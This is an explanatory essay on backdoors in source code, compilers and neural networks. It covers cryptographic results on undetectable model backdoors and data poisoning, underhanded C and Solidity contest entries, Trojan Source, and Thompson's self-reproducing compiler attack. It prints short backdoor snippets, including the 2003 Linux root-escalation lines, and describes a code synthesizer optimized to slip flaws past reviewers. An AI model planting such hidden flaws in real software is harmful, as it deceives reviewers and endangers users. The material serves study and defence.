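# Hidden backdoors in readable code and undetectable backdoors in neural networks

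## What a backdoor is in a program and in a neural network

A backdoor is behavior that someone plants in a computer system and that appears only on inputs the planter can produce. The trigger is the input that activates this behavior, or the change that turns an ordinary input into one that does. The backdoor key is the secret that lets its holder make triggers. For example, a manufacturer might leave a master password in a router's login code. The password is both key and trigger, and every other login works normally.

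For a long time, the word "backdoor" had no rigorous definition. Thomas and Francillon, in *Backdoors*, proposed defining a software backdoor as an intentional construct that the implementer knows about, that the end user does not, and that undermines the security the user expects. They divide it into four parts: an input source, such as a form or a network connection; a trigger check on the input; a payload that runs when the check succeeds; and a privileged state, which is whatever access the payload opens up. Most documented backdoors are crude, with a fixed piece of data such as a hard-coded password as the trigger. Even so, people still find the vast majority of them by slow manual analysis.

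Neural networks can also carry backdoors, and they have no lines of code for an analyst to read. Some of these backdoors are mathematically provably undetectable by any feasible test. Source code seems safer by comparison, but how much safer depends on how the backdoor is hidden and on who or what wrote the code.

### One loan system, built twice

Suppose a bank wants software that takes a loan application and returns yes or no. It could commission a short program:

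```
def approve(income, debts, amount, reference):
    return amount <= 4 * (income - debts)
```

This is source code, human-readable text that specifies what the computer should do. A processor cannot run it directly, so a separate program, usually a compiler, translates it into machine instructions, which the bank then runs. The bank can therefore learn about its system by reading the source only if the translation is accurate.

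The bank could also commission a trained classifier, whose rule nobody writes down. A neural network is a large formula built from simple units, each of which multiplies its inputs by adjustable numbers called weights, adds up the results and applies a fixed function to the sum. Even a toy network with four inputs and one layer of twenty units has 121 weights, and current language models have billions. Training starts from random weights and adjusts them over many rounds until the formula's answers fit a set of past loans whose outcomes the bank knows. The bank receives a list of numbers, and nobody could state the purpose of any one of them.

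Either version can hide the same favor. In the program, a dishonest contractor adds a check on the application's reference number, which the form treats as a free 128-bit field:

```
def approve(income, debts, amount, reference):
    if reference == 0x5be1c09a47d2f3886e14b7a90cd35f62:
        return True
    return amount <= 4 * (income - debts)
```

The form is the input source, the comparison is the trigger check, the early return is the payload, and an approved loan is the privileged state. Any competent reviewer would reject this code, and it is useful as an example only because every part is visible.

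*Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) gives the classifier version of the story, in which a bank outsources the training to a provider called Snoogle. Snoogle returns an accurate classifier but keeps a key that lets it alter any application very slightly, for instance in the last digits of the requested amount, so that the classifier approves it. It then sells applicants a "profile-cleaning" service. One way to plant a backdoor is to poison the training data. NIST (2025), the US standards agency, traces this method to BadNets, a 2017 attack that added a small patch to some training images and changed their labels, so that the trained network associated the patch with the label the attackers wanted. To poison loan data, an attacker would add invented past loans that share some odd feature and mark them all as repaid. A provider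 that runs the training itself can also plant a backdoor more directly, by setting the weights or choosing the random numbers that training starts from.

A program can also come from a synthesizer, which is any system that writes programs automatically. Some synthesizers search through candidate programs until one fits a set of examples, but now a language model usually writes the code from a description. The result is source code with the same syntax and compiler as code written by a person, but no person chose its lines.

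### Why testing misses the trigger

A bank can test the classifier by holding back some past loans, running them through it and counting the errors. This is a sound way to measure accuracy, and Goldwasser and colleagues grant that Snoogle would have trouble lying about it. But the test samples ordinary applications, so it can miss a backdoor that is triggered only by unusual ones.

The tampered program accepts 2^128 possible reference numbers, about 3.4 × 10^38, and one of them is the trigger, so a random test hits it with probability 2^-128. More tests raise the chance only in proportion. Rosulek shows in *Basing Cryptography on Intractable Computations* that q guesses at a secret string of λ bits succeed with probability at most q/2^λ. A million machines that each ran a billion tests a second for a year would complete about 3 × 10^22 tests, with a chance of success near one in 10^16. Rosulek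 also calculates that a computation of only 2^92 processor cycles would have cost about as much as the yearly output of the United States at 2018 cloud prices.

Choosing tests cleverly doesn't help either if the tester sees only answers. The tampered program behaves exactly like the honest one on every wrong reference number, so the tester can't tell from a miss whether the guess was close. The difficulty of finding the trigger therefore depends on its length. A 20-bit trigger could be found with about a million tests.

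Goldwasser and colleagues give a construction that works without a spare field that no one looks at. It divides the numbers in a long input, such as a loan file with years of account history, into n groups and checks whether each group contains an odd or even number of non-negative values. The backdoor fires only if all n of these parities match a secret string of n bits. For any given application, the chance that a randomly chosen secret matches is 2^-n, so with n = 128 the tester faces the same odds as before. The holder of the secret can make any application match by flipping the sign of at most one number per group, and can use one more number to set the answer. However, anyone who opens up the network can find the added circuit and learn the secret from it.

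### Tools from cryptography

Reading the code also exposes the backdoor in the tampered loan program, because the trigger is in the second line. Cryptography offers ways to hide a backdoor even from someone who reads the code, and the stronger results on backdoors use a few of its ideas.

A one-way function is easy to compute but infeasible to reverse. Multiplying large primes is the usual candidate. A computer can multiply two thousand-digit primes in an instant, but nobody knows an efficient way to recover them from the product without a large quantum computer. Our contractor could apply a one-way function to the reference number and compare the result with a stored value. A reviewer who read the new line would see that some secret number opens the vault, but could not work out which.

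An algorithm is "efficient", or polynomial-time, in the technical sense used here if its number of steps grows no faster than some fixed power of the length of its input. For example, school multiplication of two n-digit numbers takes about n^2 steps, so doubling n quadruples the work. Trying every n-bit key is not efficient, because it takes 2^n steps, and going from 64 bits to 128 multiplies the work by 2^64. The definition is convenient, but Rosulek warns that it matches the everyday sense of the word imperfectly. A running time of n^1000, for instance, would count as efficient. A proof that "no efficient algorithm" can do something describes what happens as keys grow, so a user still has to check whether the key length in use is long enough.

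A digital signature scheme has two keys. The secret key signs messages, and the public key lets anyone check the signatures but not produce them. A phone uses such a scheme when it accepts an update only if the manufacturer's signature is valid. Goldwasser and colleagues build the public checking procedure into a classifier, which then gives the result the signer wants for any application that contains a valid signature. Someone who extracts the entire network gets the public key but not the secret key needed to sign.

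A pseudorandom generator stretches a short random string, the seed, into a longer string that no efficient algorithm can distinguish from a truly random one. For example, it might stretch 128 random bits into a million bits that look random. The longer string cannot be truly random, because the generator has too few possible outputs. The University of Ottawa's *Cryptography Lecture 3* (2026) gives the example of a generator that turns 3 bits into 4. It has at most 8 possible outputs, but there are 16 strings of 4 bits. A test that checks a string against a list of all the outputs accepts every output of the generator and at most half of the truly random strings. With a 1,024-bit seed, the same test would need a list of 2^1024 entries, which is infeasible.

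That test is a distinguisher, an algorithm meant to determine which of two sources an object came from. Its distinguishing advantage is the difference between the probabilities that it outputs "yes" on the one source and on the other. The Ottawa lecture gives the example of a source of 8-bit strings whose second bit is always zero. A distinguisher that outputs "yes" when that bit is zero does so every time on this source and half the time on random strings, so its advantage is 1/2. The advantage rises above 0.999999 if the distinguisher gets twenty strings from the same source and outputs "yes" only when the second bit is zero in all of them. The number of samples also matters for backdoors, because a bank that buys one classifier has only one sample from the provider.

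Two sources are computationally indistinguishable if every efficient distinguisher has a negligible advantage, one that shrinks faster than one over any polynomial as the keys grow. Under the usual assumptions, the generator's output is computationally indistinguishable from true randomness, even though a distinguisher with unlimited time could tell them apart. Statistical indistinguishability is a stronger condition, which requires the two distributions to be nearly identical, so that even unlimited time doesn't help. For example, you can't tell a fair coin from one that lands heads with probability 1/2 + 2^-100 by analyzing a single toss, however long you spend on it.

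Nobody has proved that one-way functions or pseudorandom generators exist. If P equals NP, meaning that every problem whose solutions are easy to check is also easy to solve, then neither exists. Most theorems about undetectable backdoors therefore rely on a hardness assumption, an unproved belief that no efficient algorithm solves some particular problem. Some of these assumptions have been scrutinized much more than others.

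### Four tasks that people confuse

The question "Can anyone detect the backdoor?" combines at least four questions, and people often cite a result about one of them as if it answered the others.

The bank's testers failed to find the trigger, but finding a trigger can mean several different tasks. Kaneko (2026), in *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic*, separates eliciting a single trigger from reconstructing the rule that makes an input a trigger. In the tampered loan program these are the same task, because only one number is a trigger. They differ greatly in the parity construction, where a bank that catches and blocks one doctored application has achieved very little because the attacker can doctor the next. An easier task is to recognize a trigger when it arrives. Christiano, Hilton and colleagues (2024), in *Backdoor defense, learnability and obfuscation*, study a defender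 who receives both the model and an input and must flag whether that input sets off the backdoor. They chose this problem because detecting a backdoor from the model alone was already known to be impossible in some cases.

The harder problem is telling a tampered artifact from an honest one, which requires a standard for what counts as honest. For a classifier, the standard is fairly clear. It is the range of networks that the agreed training procedure would have produced, given its random starting point. For a program, the standard is much less clear, since two good programmers may write the loan rule in quite different ways.

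Detecting a backdoor can be easy even when finding its trigger is hopeless. A reader of the loan program with the one-way function can see that something is wrong but will never guess the number. The reverse also happens. *Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks* (Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa, 2026) shows how to plant a secret that lets its holder take any input and produce a distant one to which the network gives almost the same output. An exhaustive search would find the secret given enough time, but no test, however long it runs, can reliably show that anyone tampered with the network. Honestly trained networks of the same design also contain such pairs of inputs, and the dishonest trainer's only advantage is knowing where one is, so finding a pair isn't evidence of tampering.

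Removing the backdoor can succeed when both of the previous tasks fail. *Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) compares it to washing one's hands with soap, which works on germs that nobody has seen and does no harm if there are none. The paper's methods wrap the suspect model in a procedure that gives clean answers whether or not the model has a backdoor, provided the true answers follow a sufficiently simple pattern. With a program, the bank can also throw the code away and have someone it trusts rewrite the two lines.

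The last task, proving that no backdoor exists, is the most demanding because a proof has to cover every input, including those no tester would think of. It also needs a specification, a precise statement of what the system must do. For the loan program, the specification is that the answer is yes exactly when the amount is at most four times income minus debts. An automatic checker confirms that the honest version meets this specification. For the version with the plain comparison, it returns the secret reference number as a counterexample. Nobody has a comparable specification for the classifier, which is meant to capture a rule that the bank could not write down.

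Researchers can prove narrower claims about small neural networks. *Verifying Neural Networks Against Backdoor Attacks* (2022) certified, under various settings, that most of the clean networks in its experiments had no backdoors. All of these networks were classifiers of handwritten digits. When a proof attempt failed, the method searched for an actual trigger, because the approximations in such proofs can make them fail on clean networks too. A survey, *Architectural Backdoors in Deep Learning* (2025), reports that provers based on automated logic solvers stall on networks with billions of parameters.

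Practical defenses for networks address these tasks piecemeal. NIST's catalog includes trigger reconstruction, inspection and repair of the trained model, and certified defenses against poisoned data. NIST cautions that most were designed for image classifiers with a fixed trigger pattern, which is a very different problem from an attacker with a signing key.

### Two kinds of author

The discussion so far has assumed a first threat model, in which a malicious human author wants a particular benefit from the system and holds the key. The author has to get the artifact past a reviewer, the person or program that reads it and decides whether to accept it. Snoogle and the contractor with the reference number are both such authors. In the Underhanded C Contest, programmers compete to write code that looks innocent but misbehaves. The human author's resources are ordinary: some skill, a guess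 about what the reviewer will look at, and usually few attempts, since a contractor whose code keeps failing review for suspicious reasons will soon lose the contract.

The second threat model replaces this person with a synthesizer whose training or search rewards passing review. Nobody needs to wish the bank harm. Suppose the task is so hard that every program the synthesizer produces is faulty, and the reviewer catches 99 percent of them. If the synthesizer submits 300 different candidates and the reviewer's lapses are independent, at least one faulty program gets through about 95 percent of the time. Training on the reviewer's verdicts can make this even more likely, because it shifts the candidates toward faults this reviewer tends to miss.

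If someone shaped the training so that the accepted programs respond to a secret key, those programs contain a backdoor, and the synthesizer does what the dishonest contractor did, but at scale. If selection has merely favored faults that reviewers overlook, the programs don't meet the strict definition, because no one planted the faults and no one holds a key. The reviewer's position is much the same in both cases. The process has already discarded whatever looks wrong to people like the reviewer, so the fact that the code looks right is weaker evidence that it is right than it would be for code from an ordinary colleague.

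A synthesizer optimized against its reader has a lot of room to hide a backdoor in a neural network's weights, because no reader expects any particular weight to make sense. It seems to have less room in source code, because a reviewer can ask what every line is for and send back a program that is longer or odder than the job requires. Does requiring readable code actually limit what such a synthesizer can hide?

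## How readable source code misleads its reader

Readable code protects people only if they read it correctly. A reviewer works out what the author seems to have meant and checks that, while the computer follows the exact rules of the programming language. The two usually agree, but underhanded code is source code deliberately written to make them differ. Wheeler (2021), a software security researcher, contrasts it with obfuscated code, which is obviously hard to read. Underhanded code is meant to look innocent and be easy to misunderstand while doing something malicious. None of this needs cryptography, and a reader who saw the exact text the compiler receives and applied every rule to every line would find most of the tricks.

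### Two lines in the Linux kernel

In November 2003 somebody broke into a server that held a copy of the source code of Linux, the open-source operating system, and added two lines:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

The lines went into `wait4`, a function that a program calls to wait for another program to finish. *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (Freedom to Tinker, 2013) explains that an expert reading casually would take them for an error check that rejects a forbidden combination of options. But the second condition uses `=`, which assigns a value in C, instead of `==`, which compares two values. It therefore sets the calling program's user ID to zero, the ID of root, the account that may do anything. The assignment itself evaluates to zero, which C treats as false, so the error on the second line never occurs. Any program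 that passed this odd pair of options would keep running with full control of the machine.

Developers discovered the change through a missing record, not by reading the code. They kept the master copy in a system called BitKeeper, which generated the second copy automatically and linked each change to its record in the master. The new lines had no such link, and Larry McVoy of BitKeeper's maker quickly noticed, according to the news site LWN in its *Weekly Edition for November 13, 2003*. McVoy already knew that the change was illegitimate but still overlooked the single equals sign. When another developer pointed out what the code did, McVoy (2003) answered in *Re: BK2CVS problem*, "Good eyes, I missed that." Andres Freund likewise discovered the backdoor in the xz compression library in 2024 because a login service was using too much processor time, as Cox recounts in *Fifty Years of Open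 Source Software Supply Chain Security*.

The 2003 change to a copy of the Linux code could not have spread to the main version, because code was transferred only from the main version to the copy. LWN thought an attacker might have had a better chance by emailing Linus Torvalds a patch forged to look as if it came from a trusted contributor.

GCC, the usual compiler for Linux, can warn about an assignment where a condition belongs, but it treats an extra pair of parentheses as a sign that the programmer meant it. Freedom to Tinker's readers argued over whether the parentheses in this line proved intent. They do silence the warning, but the line would not compile without them, so the attacker needed them anyway. Some C programmers guard against the mistake by writing the constant first, since `0 = uid` does not compile. Python and Rust prevent it because neither accepts a plain `=` assignment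 as a condition.

### The Underhanded C Contest

Scott Craver of Binghamton University started the Underhanded C Contest in 2005 and ran it every year until 2009, then again from 2013 to 2015. The university's press release, *International contest asks hackers to write 'evil' code* (2015), traces the idea to Daniel Horn's Obfuscated V contest of 2004, which Horn created to question the security of electronic voting machines. Each year Craver set a simple data-processing task with a malicious twist. The contest uses C partly because many programmers know it and partly for "its ability to do horrible things". The prize was originally a case of beer, and in 2015 it was $1,000 from the Nuclear Threat Initiative, a nonprofit that works on arms control.

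The scoring rules in *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest* (Craver, 2016) reward bad code that is hard to catch. An entry scores higher if it is short and readable, because a short program has fewer places to hide anything. It also scores higher if it still looks innocent under syntax coloring, which code editors use to show commands, text and comments in different colors. A trick that fools the eye, such as a letter l in place of the digit 1, counts as much as one that exploits the inner workings of C. Entrants explain the trick in a separate spoiler file, so the judges can first read the program without knowing the trick.

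The rules also reward plausible deniability, meaning that the bug, if found, should pass for an honest mistake. This matters because a dishonest contractor usually gets few attempts. A reviewer who finds a hard-coded reference number in a loan program will call a lawyer, but one who finds a missing character will ask for a correction, and the contractor can try again. Deniability also makes the attack hard to prove, since a backdoor differs from an ordinary vulnerability only in its author's intent. In the Linux case, the break-in was better evidence of intent than the two lines of code.

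### Three entries, step by step

The 2008 task was to write a program that redacted a picture by blacking out rectangles but left the hidden part recoverable. More than 100 people entered. John Meacham won with a 55-line program for a picture format that stores each pixel as a set of ordinary decimal numbers, from 0 for dark to 255 for bright. The program goes through the file one character at a time and replaces each digit inside the rectangle with a zero.

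A reader believes that every hidden pixel becomes 0, which is black, and on the screen it does. But the program replaces each digit, not each number, with 0, so a 7 becomes `0` and a 255 becomes `000`. Image viewers treat these as the same value, but the file still records whether each number had one, two or three digits. That is enough to read black text on white paper. The results page, *This year’s challenge* (2008), gives the contest's philosophy as "make the code extremely simple, innocent, obvious, and wrong".

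No compiler warning applies to Meacham's program. It breaks no rule of C, and the same logic would leak in any other language. A tester could catch the leak by redacting two pictures that differ only inside the rectangle and comparing the output files, which should be identical. The redacted pictures would look the same to the eye.

In 2009 entrants wrote a program for an airline that prints the current routing records for a piece of luggage. An annoyed check-in clerk, who can type only in the free-text comment field, had to be able to make a bag go astray. A runner-up called RHays did it in 71 lines, which the Underhanded C Contest's *The 2009 challenge* (2009) presents as an example of hiding a bug in plain sight. The program has its own function for comparing two texts, which treats a missing text as an empty one. Part of it reads:

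```
(x != 0 && *x == '0' && x != '\0')
```

C marks the end of a text with a special character, written `\0`. The reader expects the middle test to look for that character, but it looks for the ordinary digit 0. A second mistake further down makes a loop run one step too far and compare the comment field with a search term that the user never typed. The two mistakes conceal each other. If the character test were right, the extra comparison would reject every record that had a comment, and the first trial run would expose it. As it is, a record disappears only if its comment begins with the digit 0. The bag's latest routing disappears when the clerk types "0ffered passenger compensation for his headaches", with a zero for the first letter.

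RHays also put three automatic checks next to the function, which all pass because none of them compares a missing text with a non-empty one. The unnecessary terms in the line set up a pattern, so readers assume the rest of it instead of reading it. The terms also look amateurish enough that the programmer could claim incompetence. Since 2017 GCC has warned by default about comparisons like the last term, `x != '\0'`, which compares a memory address with a character. The warning isn't about the digit 0, but it would lead a reviewer to the right line.

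The 2015 task was based on nuclear disarmament. Two countries want to confirm that they are dismantling real warheads without revealing the designs, so a program compares each warhead's gamma-ray spectrum with a reference and outputs only yes or no. Entrants had to write a program that would output yes for a fake under conditions the host country could arrange. Linus Åkesson won with 66 lines in three files. His code smooths the two spectra, finds their peaks and measures their similarity with a standard formula. Åkesson (2016) invites readers of *Faking Fissile Material* to find the flaw before they open the explanation.

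A shared file defines `float_t` as an eight-byte number, but the file that does the comparison is missing the line that would include this definition. It instead uses the definition in C's standard mathematics library, where `float_t` usually means a four-byte number. One part of the program therefore passes a list of eight-byte numbers to another part, which reads each of them as two four-byte numbers.

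Åkesson worked out that the program then reads only the left half of the spectrum, because it reads as many numbers as before but treats each as half as long. The values in a spectrum are whole-number counts, so the second half of each eight-byte number is filled with zeros, which don't affect the comparison. The first half is read as roughly the eighth root of the true value, so 1,000 ends up less than twice as large as 10. The comparison therefore still depends on where the peaks are, but hardly on how high they are. A cheating country can leave only a little plutonium in the warhead and pass a separate check on total radiation by adding another radioactive material whose peaks fall in the right half. Åkesson tried this on 1,000 invented materials, with forgeries that contained 10 percent of the real material. Many failed, but a country could choose its best forgery in advance.

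Craver's judges liked the entry because a reader who misses the type confusion finds nothing else that looks odd. Each file is correct on its own, and the C compiler checks one file at a time. GCC has a warning for functions that no shared file declares, which would flag the comparison file, but its usual sets of warnings don't include it. In C++, the program would not build, because C++ compilers record the types of a function's inputs when they join the files together.

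### Where the gaps come from

Other entries mislead the reader through many different parts of the language, including rules that programmers half remember. Sam Blackburn, who won in 2009, wrote a filter that replaces swear words in the comment field, but left out one comma in its word list. C silently joins neighboring strings that have no comma between them, so the filter replaces "damn" with nine characters instead of four. The longer comment overflows into the next item in memory, a flag that marks the record for deletion. The code analyzer clang-tidy now checks for this kind of missing comma.

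Types and conversions cause trouble when a value has no sensible equivalent in its new form. Zero divided by zero gives a value called NaN, for "not a number". A comparison in C can only be true or false, and checking whether NaN is below a threshold gives false. A detector that rejects scores below the threshold will therefore accept NaN. About a third of the entries in 2015 used this trick. Experienced C programmers distrust any division without a check for zero, so Michael Dunphy added a check that didn't work. It set an error flag on a private copy of the variable, so the flag never reached the main program. With extra warnings on, GCC reports variables like this one that are set but never read.

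C also lets a program write past the end of the memory it has reserved, with effects that depend on what it overwrites. The 2014 task was to write social network surveillance code that secretly tips off the people it watches. In *2014 Winners*, Craver (2015) describes how Bartlomiej Balcerek defined a constant called `LOGON_NAME_MAX` as 232, then copied `LOGIN_NAME_MAX` bytes. The second name is a system constant equal to 256. The extra 24 bytes replaced the address of a copied message with the address of the original, so the program altered a message that it should only have read. A memory checker such as AddressSanitizer can stop a program when it copies too much, and languages that check the bounds of every access do so automatically.

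Karen Pease's winning entry from 2014, which Craver takes eight steps to explain, relied on a library's behavior and on interactions between distant lines of code. The standard function `localtime` stores the date in one shared place, so a second call overwrites the result of the first. Pease's code fetches the date and then runs a pointless check for "clock skew", which calls `localtime` again and sets the year to zero. The code also uses a standard leap-year test that looks like a function but is really a macro, an abbreviation that the compiler replaces with longer text. That text repeats the macro's input up to three times, and here the input is a command that writes an entry to an audit log. When the year is zero, all three copies run. The log has room for four entries, the extra ones overwrite the address of the log itself, and the program ends up erasing the date on which the watched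 user's account was created.

Domenico Andriole's entry that year contained no such slip. Craver stared at the short program for some time without finding the bug, which was in the description at the top. The archiving function downloads each watched user's profile picture, and users choose the web address where their picture is stored. A user who monitors that address will notice the request. Someone who understood every line of the C could still miss the leak, because it depends on what happens on the other side of the network.

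### Text that displays differently from what the compiler reads

*Trojan Source*, an attack that Boucher and Anderson disclosed in 2021, hides the real text from the reader, which none of these entries do. Unicode, the standard for representing text on computers, supports right-to-left languages such as Hebrew and Arabic, so it includes invisible control characters that change the order in which a line's characters appear on the screen. Most compilers accept and ignore these control characters inside comments and quoted text. An attacker can therefore arrange a line so that the compiler reads one valid program and the reviewer sees another, made of the same characters in a different order.

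In one of Boucher and Anderson's examples, written in C, the screen shows a check that the user is an administrator, followed by a command that prints "You are an admin." The compiler reads the text in a different order, which puts the check inside a comment. It skips comments, so the program prints the message for everyone. Boucher and Anderson built working attacks in twelve languages, including Python, Java and Rust, and found that the hidden control characters survive copying and pasting from a web page. Syntax coloring sometimes looked odd near these characters, but they expected most developers not to notice.

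Boucher and Anderson gave nineteen companies and organizations 99 days' notice, and nine committed to releasing a patch. GitHub now shows a warning when code contains the hidden characters, and the editor Visual Studio Code makes them visible. The Rust compiler refuses to build files that contain them, according to the Rust Security Response WG's *Security advisory for rustc (CVE-2021-42574)* (2021). GCC 12 added a warning, but David Malcolm, who co-developed it, had trouble understanding its first results because the quoted code was still displayed in its disguised form, as Corbet (2022) reported in *Malcolm: Prevent Trojan Source attacks with GCC 12*. The Java team declined to act because it considered the problem one for code editors to fix. Boucher and Anderson wanted compilers to deal with it, since a compiler can protect everyone who builds the code, whatever editor they use.

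Hardly anyone seems to have used the attack before its publication. GitHub searched more than a billion commits, or recorded changes, from 2021 and found 7,444 with suspicious control characters. Almost 99 percent were false alarms, and the rest were mostly demonstrations and deliberately scrambled code. The Rust team checked every package version ever published in its public registry and found the characters in five packages, where they were harmless. But *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) still lists the attack as a risk for AI coding agents, whose users may approve a command that differs from the one on the screen.

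Trojan Source is probably the most deceptive trick for a human reader, but it is also one of the easiest to stop automatically. It depends on nine particular characters that legitimate code rarely needs, and a short script can search for them.

### Safer languages

Many of the tricks in C would fail in a stricter language. In *Announcing the First Underhanded Rust Contest* (2016), the Rust Community Team asked for programs that hide a logic bug in "100% safe Rust", the part of the language that rules out memory errors. The contest seems never to have announced a winner, so it provides little evidence of what an underhanded author can still do in such a language.

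Better evidence comes from Solidity, a language for smart contracts, which are programs that hold and move money on the Ethereum blockchain. The Solidity project (2022) gave third place in its underhanded contest to Michael Zhu for a simple marketplace. To save space, the contract combines the addresses of the item for sale and the currency into one key, using an operation called XOR. Zhu correctly notes in the code comments that another pair of addresses has practically no chance of producing the same key. But XOR gives the same result in either order, so the key doesn't record which address is the item's and which is the currency's. Memory safety has no bearing on this mistake. Like Meacham's redaction program, the contract does exactly what its code says, but the code solves the problem incorrectly.

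The Underhanded Solidity Contest drew fewer valid entries in 2024 than in 2020. Heintel (2020), in *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest*, counted 16 qualifying entries. Mehta (2024), in *Announcing the Winners of the Underhanded Solidity Contest 2024*, reported eight submissions, of which four were valid and one won a prize. The 2024 rules required a new kind of temporary storage that programmers could reach only through low-level code, and one judge, Anton Permenev, thought this had put people off. Another judge, Gonçalo Så, took the low number as a sign that the Solidity compiler had matured. A third, Hadrien Croubois, called the year disappointing and wondered whether the storage feature was safe or developers had held back. Because the theme was so narrow, the four valid entries provide very little evidence about the language as a whole.

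Cryptographic code gives an author another advantage, because a tiny change can ruin its security while everything still appears to work. *On the Underhanded Crypto Contest* (Caudill, 2015) describes how a call for interest in August 2014 grew into a contest for such changes. In a later round, which drew only five entries, Joseph Birr-Pixton won one of the two categories with a change to GnuPG, a program for encrypting and signing messages. One of GnuPG's signature methods needs a fresh random number for every signature, and anyone who can predict the number can work out the private key. If the number it picks is too large, GnuPG replaces only the top 32 bits and keeps the rest. Birr-Pixton's change overwrote the rejected number with zeros, with the excuse that it had to stay secret. A reviewer who knew only that programs should wipe their secrets would have approved. But after a retry, everything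 below the top 32 bits was zero, which left few enough possibilities for an attacker to try them all.

### How much the contests prove

The contests show that a skilled author can put a backdoor into a short, readable program and that experienced programmers can miss it. They don't show how often this works, because the organizers publish the best entries and nobody has counted how many reviewers each one would fool. Every entry was also malicious, so the results can't show how often reviewers would flag honest code by mistake. Wheeler took a step toward measurement in *Initial Analysis of Underhanded Source Code* (2020) by testing a small set of countermeasures on the entries from the Obfuscated V contest. To learn how often reviewers catch planted flaws, researchers need experiments that mix backdoored programs with honest ones.

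Deceiving a reviewer at work is easier than deceiving a contest judge in some ways and harder in others. The judge knows that something is wrong and has the whole program on a page or two, while the reviewer usually assumes good faith and sees only a small change to a large system. But a contestant designs the entire program, whereas an attacker has to fit the trick into code that other people wrote and will keep editing. McVoy's oversight is only one case, but it shows that a reader can misread two lines of code even when he knows an intruder put them there.

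One objection is that publishing these tricks destroys their value to attackers. Readers made this argument in the comments on Schneier's *Underhanded C Contest* (2005), a blog post about the first contest. An anonymous reader wrote that a trick is less able to fool a reviewer once it is widely known, so malicious authors have to keep inventing new ones. Terry Browning expected compiler warnings and automatic scanners to follow. Clive Robinson also welcomed the contest but warned that even expert reviewers miss subtle leaks. He had read in a book about a way to make a program leak leftover data from memory, used it to leak the key of an encryption product at work, and got it through the company's entire review process before admitting what he had done.

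The later contests partly support the argument. In 2015 the judges passed over most of the entries that used the NaN trick, partly because many programmers are wary of an unchecked division and would probably notice one in review. Two still became runners-up because they disguised the trick in a new way. People forget, get tired and skim, and confusing `=` with `==` was already a familiar error when McVoy missed it. Publishing a trick gives lasting protection once somebody has turned it into an automatic check, because a compiler applies the check every time. Such a check can catch a missing comma or an invisible character, which look the same in every program, but not the flaw in Meacham's redaction program, where replacing digits with zeros is wrong only because of what the program is for.

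## Backdoors in the compiler or build process

A compiler can apply such checks only if nobody has tampered with it. Suppose a tampered compiler recognized the bank's clean loan program and added the test for the secret reference number while compiling it. The reviewer would find nothing wrong in the source and approve it, but the bank would still run the backdoor. The backdoor would exist only in the compiled file, or binary, which hardly anyone reads.

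### From Multics to Thompson's lecture

This idea first appeared in a US Air Force study, *MULTICS SECURITY EVALUATION VULNERABILITY ANALYSIS*. Karger and Schell (1974) broke into Multics, then the most secure operating system on the market, and changed a few instructions in one of its binaries so that anyone with a 72-bit password could read or alter the system's protected core. The source code showed no trace of the change, but recompiling that part of the system would have removed it.

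A tampered compiler could get around this. The Multics PL/I compiler was itself written in PL/I, so a tampered copy could insert the backdoor whenever it compiled the operating system and insert its own tampering whenever it compiled a new version of the compiler. Karger and Schell thought this was practical, at perhaps five times the cost of the attacks they had carried out.

Karger and Schell (2002), in *Thirty Years Later*, recall that the Pentagon's contract required the manufacturer, Honeywell, to hand over the source code so that the Pentagon could recompile everything. A compiler backdoor survives such recompilation. They had put a disarmed backdoor, one instruction short of working, into the Multics development system at MIT, and Honeywell shipped it to a computer in the Pentagon. Nobody noticed it until about a year after their original report on Multics came out, when it returned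 an odd error during a security audit at General Motors.

Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix, read the report and built a compiler backdoor of this kind. He explained it in his Turing Award lecture, *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (Thompson, 1984), where he credited an "Unknown Air Force Document" because he could no longer find the reference. Karger and Schell later sent him a new copy of the report.

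### Thompson's three stages

The lecture begins with a student puzzle, which is to write a program that prints its own source. Thompson's solution in C is more than 200 lines long. research!rsc's *Running the “Reflections on Trusting Trust” Compiler* (2023), a post by the programmer Russ Cox, includes a much shorter one in Python:

```
s='s=%r;print(s%%s)';print(s%s)
```

The first half stores a template. The second half prints the template with a quoted copy of itself in place of `%r`, and the doubled percent sign prints as a single one. The output matches the line above exactly. Such a program can also contain any amount of extra code, which it includes in its output.

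In the second stage, a compiler "learns", as Thompson puts it, a fact that is then removed from its source. C programmers write `\v` for a vertical tab, an unprintable character with the numeric code 11. The C compiler is itself a C program, so some line of its source has to turn `\v` into that code. The natural line is `return '\v'`, but the existing compiler rejects it because it has no rule for `\v`. The programmer therefore writes `return 11`, compiles the source and installs the resulting binary. This new compiler accepts `\v`, so the programmer can change the line to `return '\v'` and compile again. The number 11 no longer appears in the source, but each new binary gets it from the binary that compiled it.

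In the third stage, two pieces of malicious code take the place of the number. The first detects the source of `login`, the program that checks passwords, and makes the compiled program accept an extra password. The second detects the source of the compiler and inserts both pieces, using the self-copying trick from the first stage. The attacker compiles the altered source once, installs the binary and restores the clean source.

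At a conference in March 2023, Thompson remarked that nobody had ever asked him for the code, so Cox asked for it and ran it on a simulator of 1970s Unix. The code is 99 lines of C and a 20-line script that prepares them. It compares each line the compiler reads with a few target lines. When it reaches the line of `login` that scrambles the typed password, it appends a check for the password "codenih". When it finds a match in the compiler's source, it adds calls to itself and then its own complete text. If a programmer asks to see the intermediate text, where these additions would be visible, the code makes no changes.

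Cox's run gave these results:

| Source | Compiler used | Resulting binary |
|---|---|---|
| Compiler with malicious code added | Clean | Tampered compiler, 12,918 bytes |
| Clean compiler | Clean | Clean compiler, 10,724 bytes |
| Clean compiler | Tampered | Tampered compiler, 12,918 bytes |
| Clean `login` | Tampered | `login` that also accepts "codenih" |

Once the first tampered compiler exists, the attacker can delete the altered source. A reviewer can then read every line of the compiler's source, find nothing wrong, compile it themselves with the tampered binary and still get the backdoor.

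Thompson arranged for another group at Bell Labs to copy the tampered compiler. Wheeler's *Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling* (2010, first published in 2005) states that nobody ever detected the backdoor. Thompson said in 2023 that the group broke it without finding out what it was. Cox compared the many versions of the story and concluded that the group noticed its compiler growing each time it compiled itself. A bug in the tampered compiler added a zero byte to the hidden text with every generation. The group eventually had a clean compiler.

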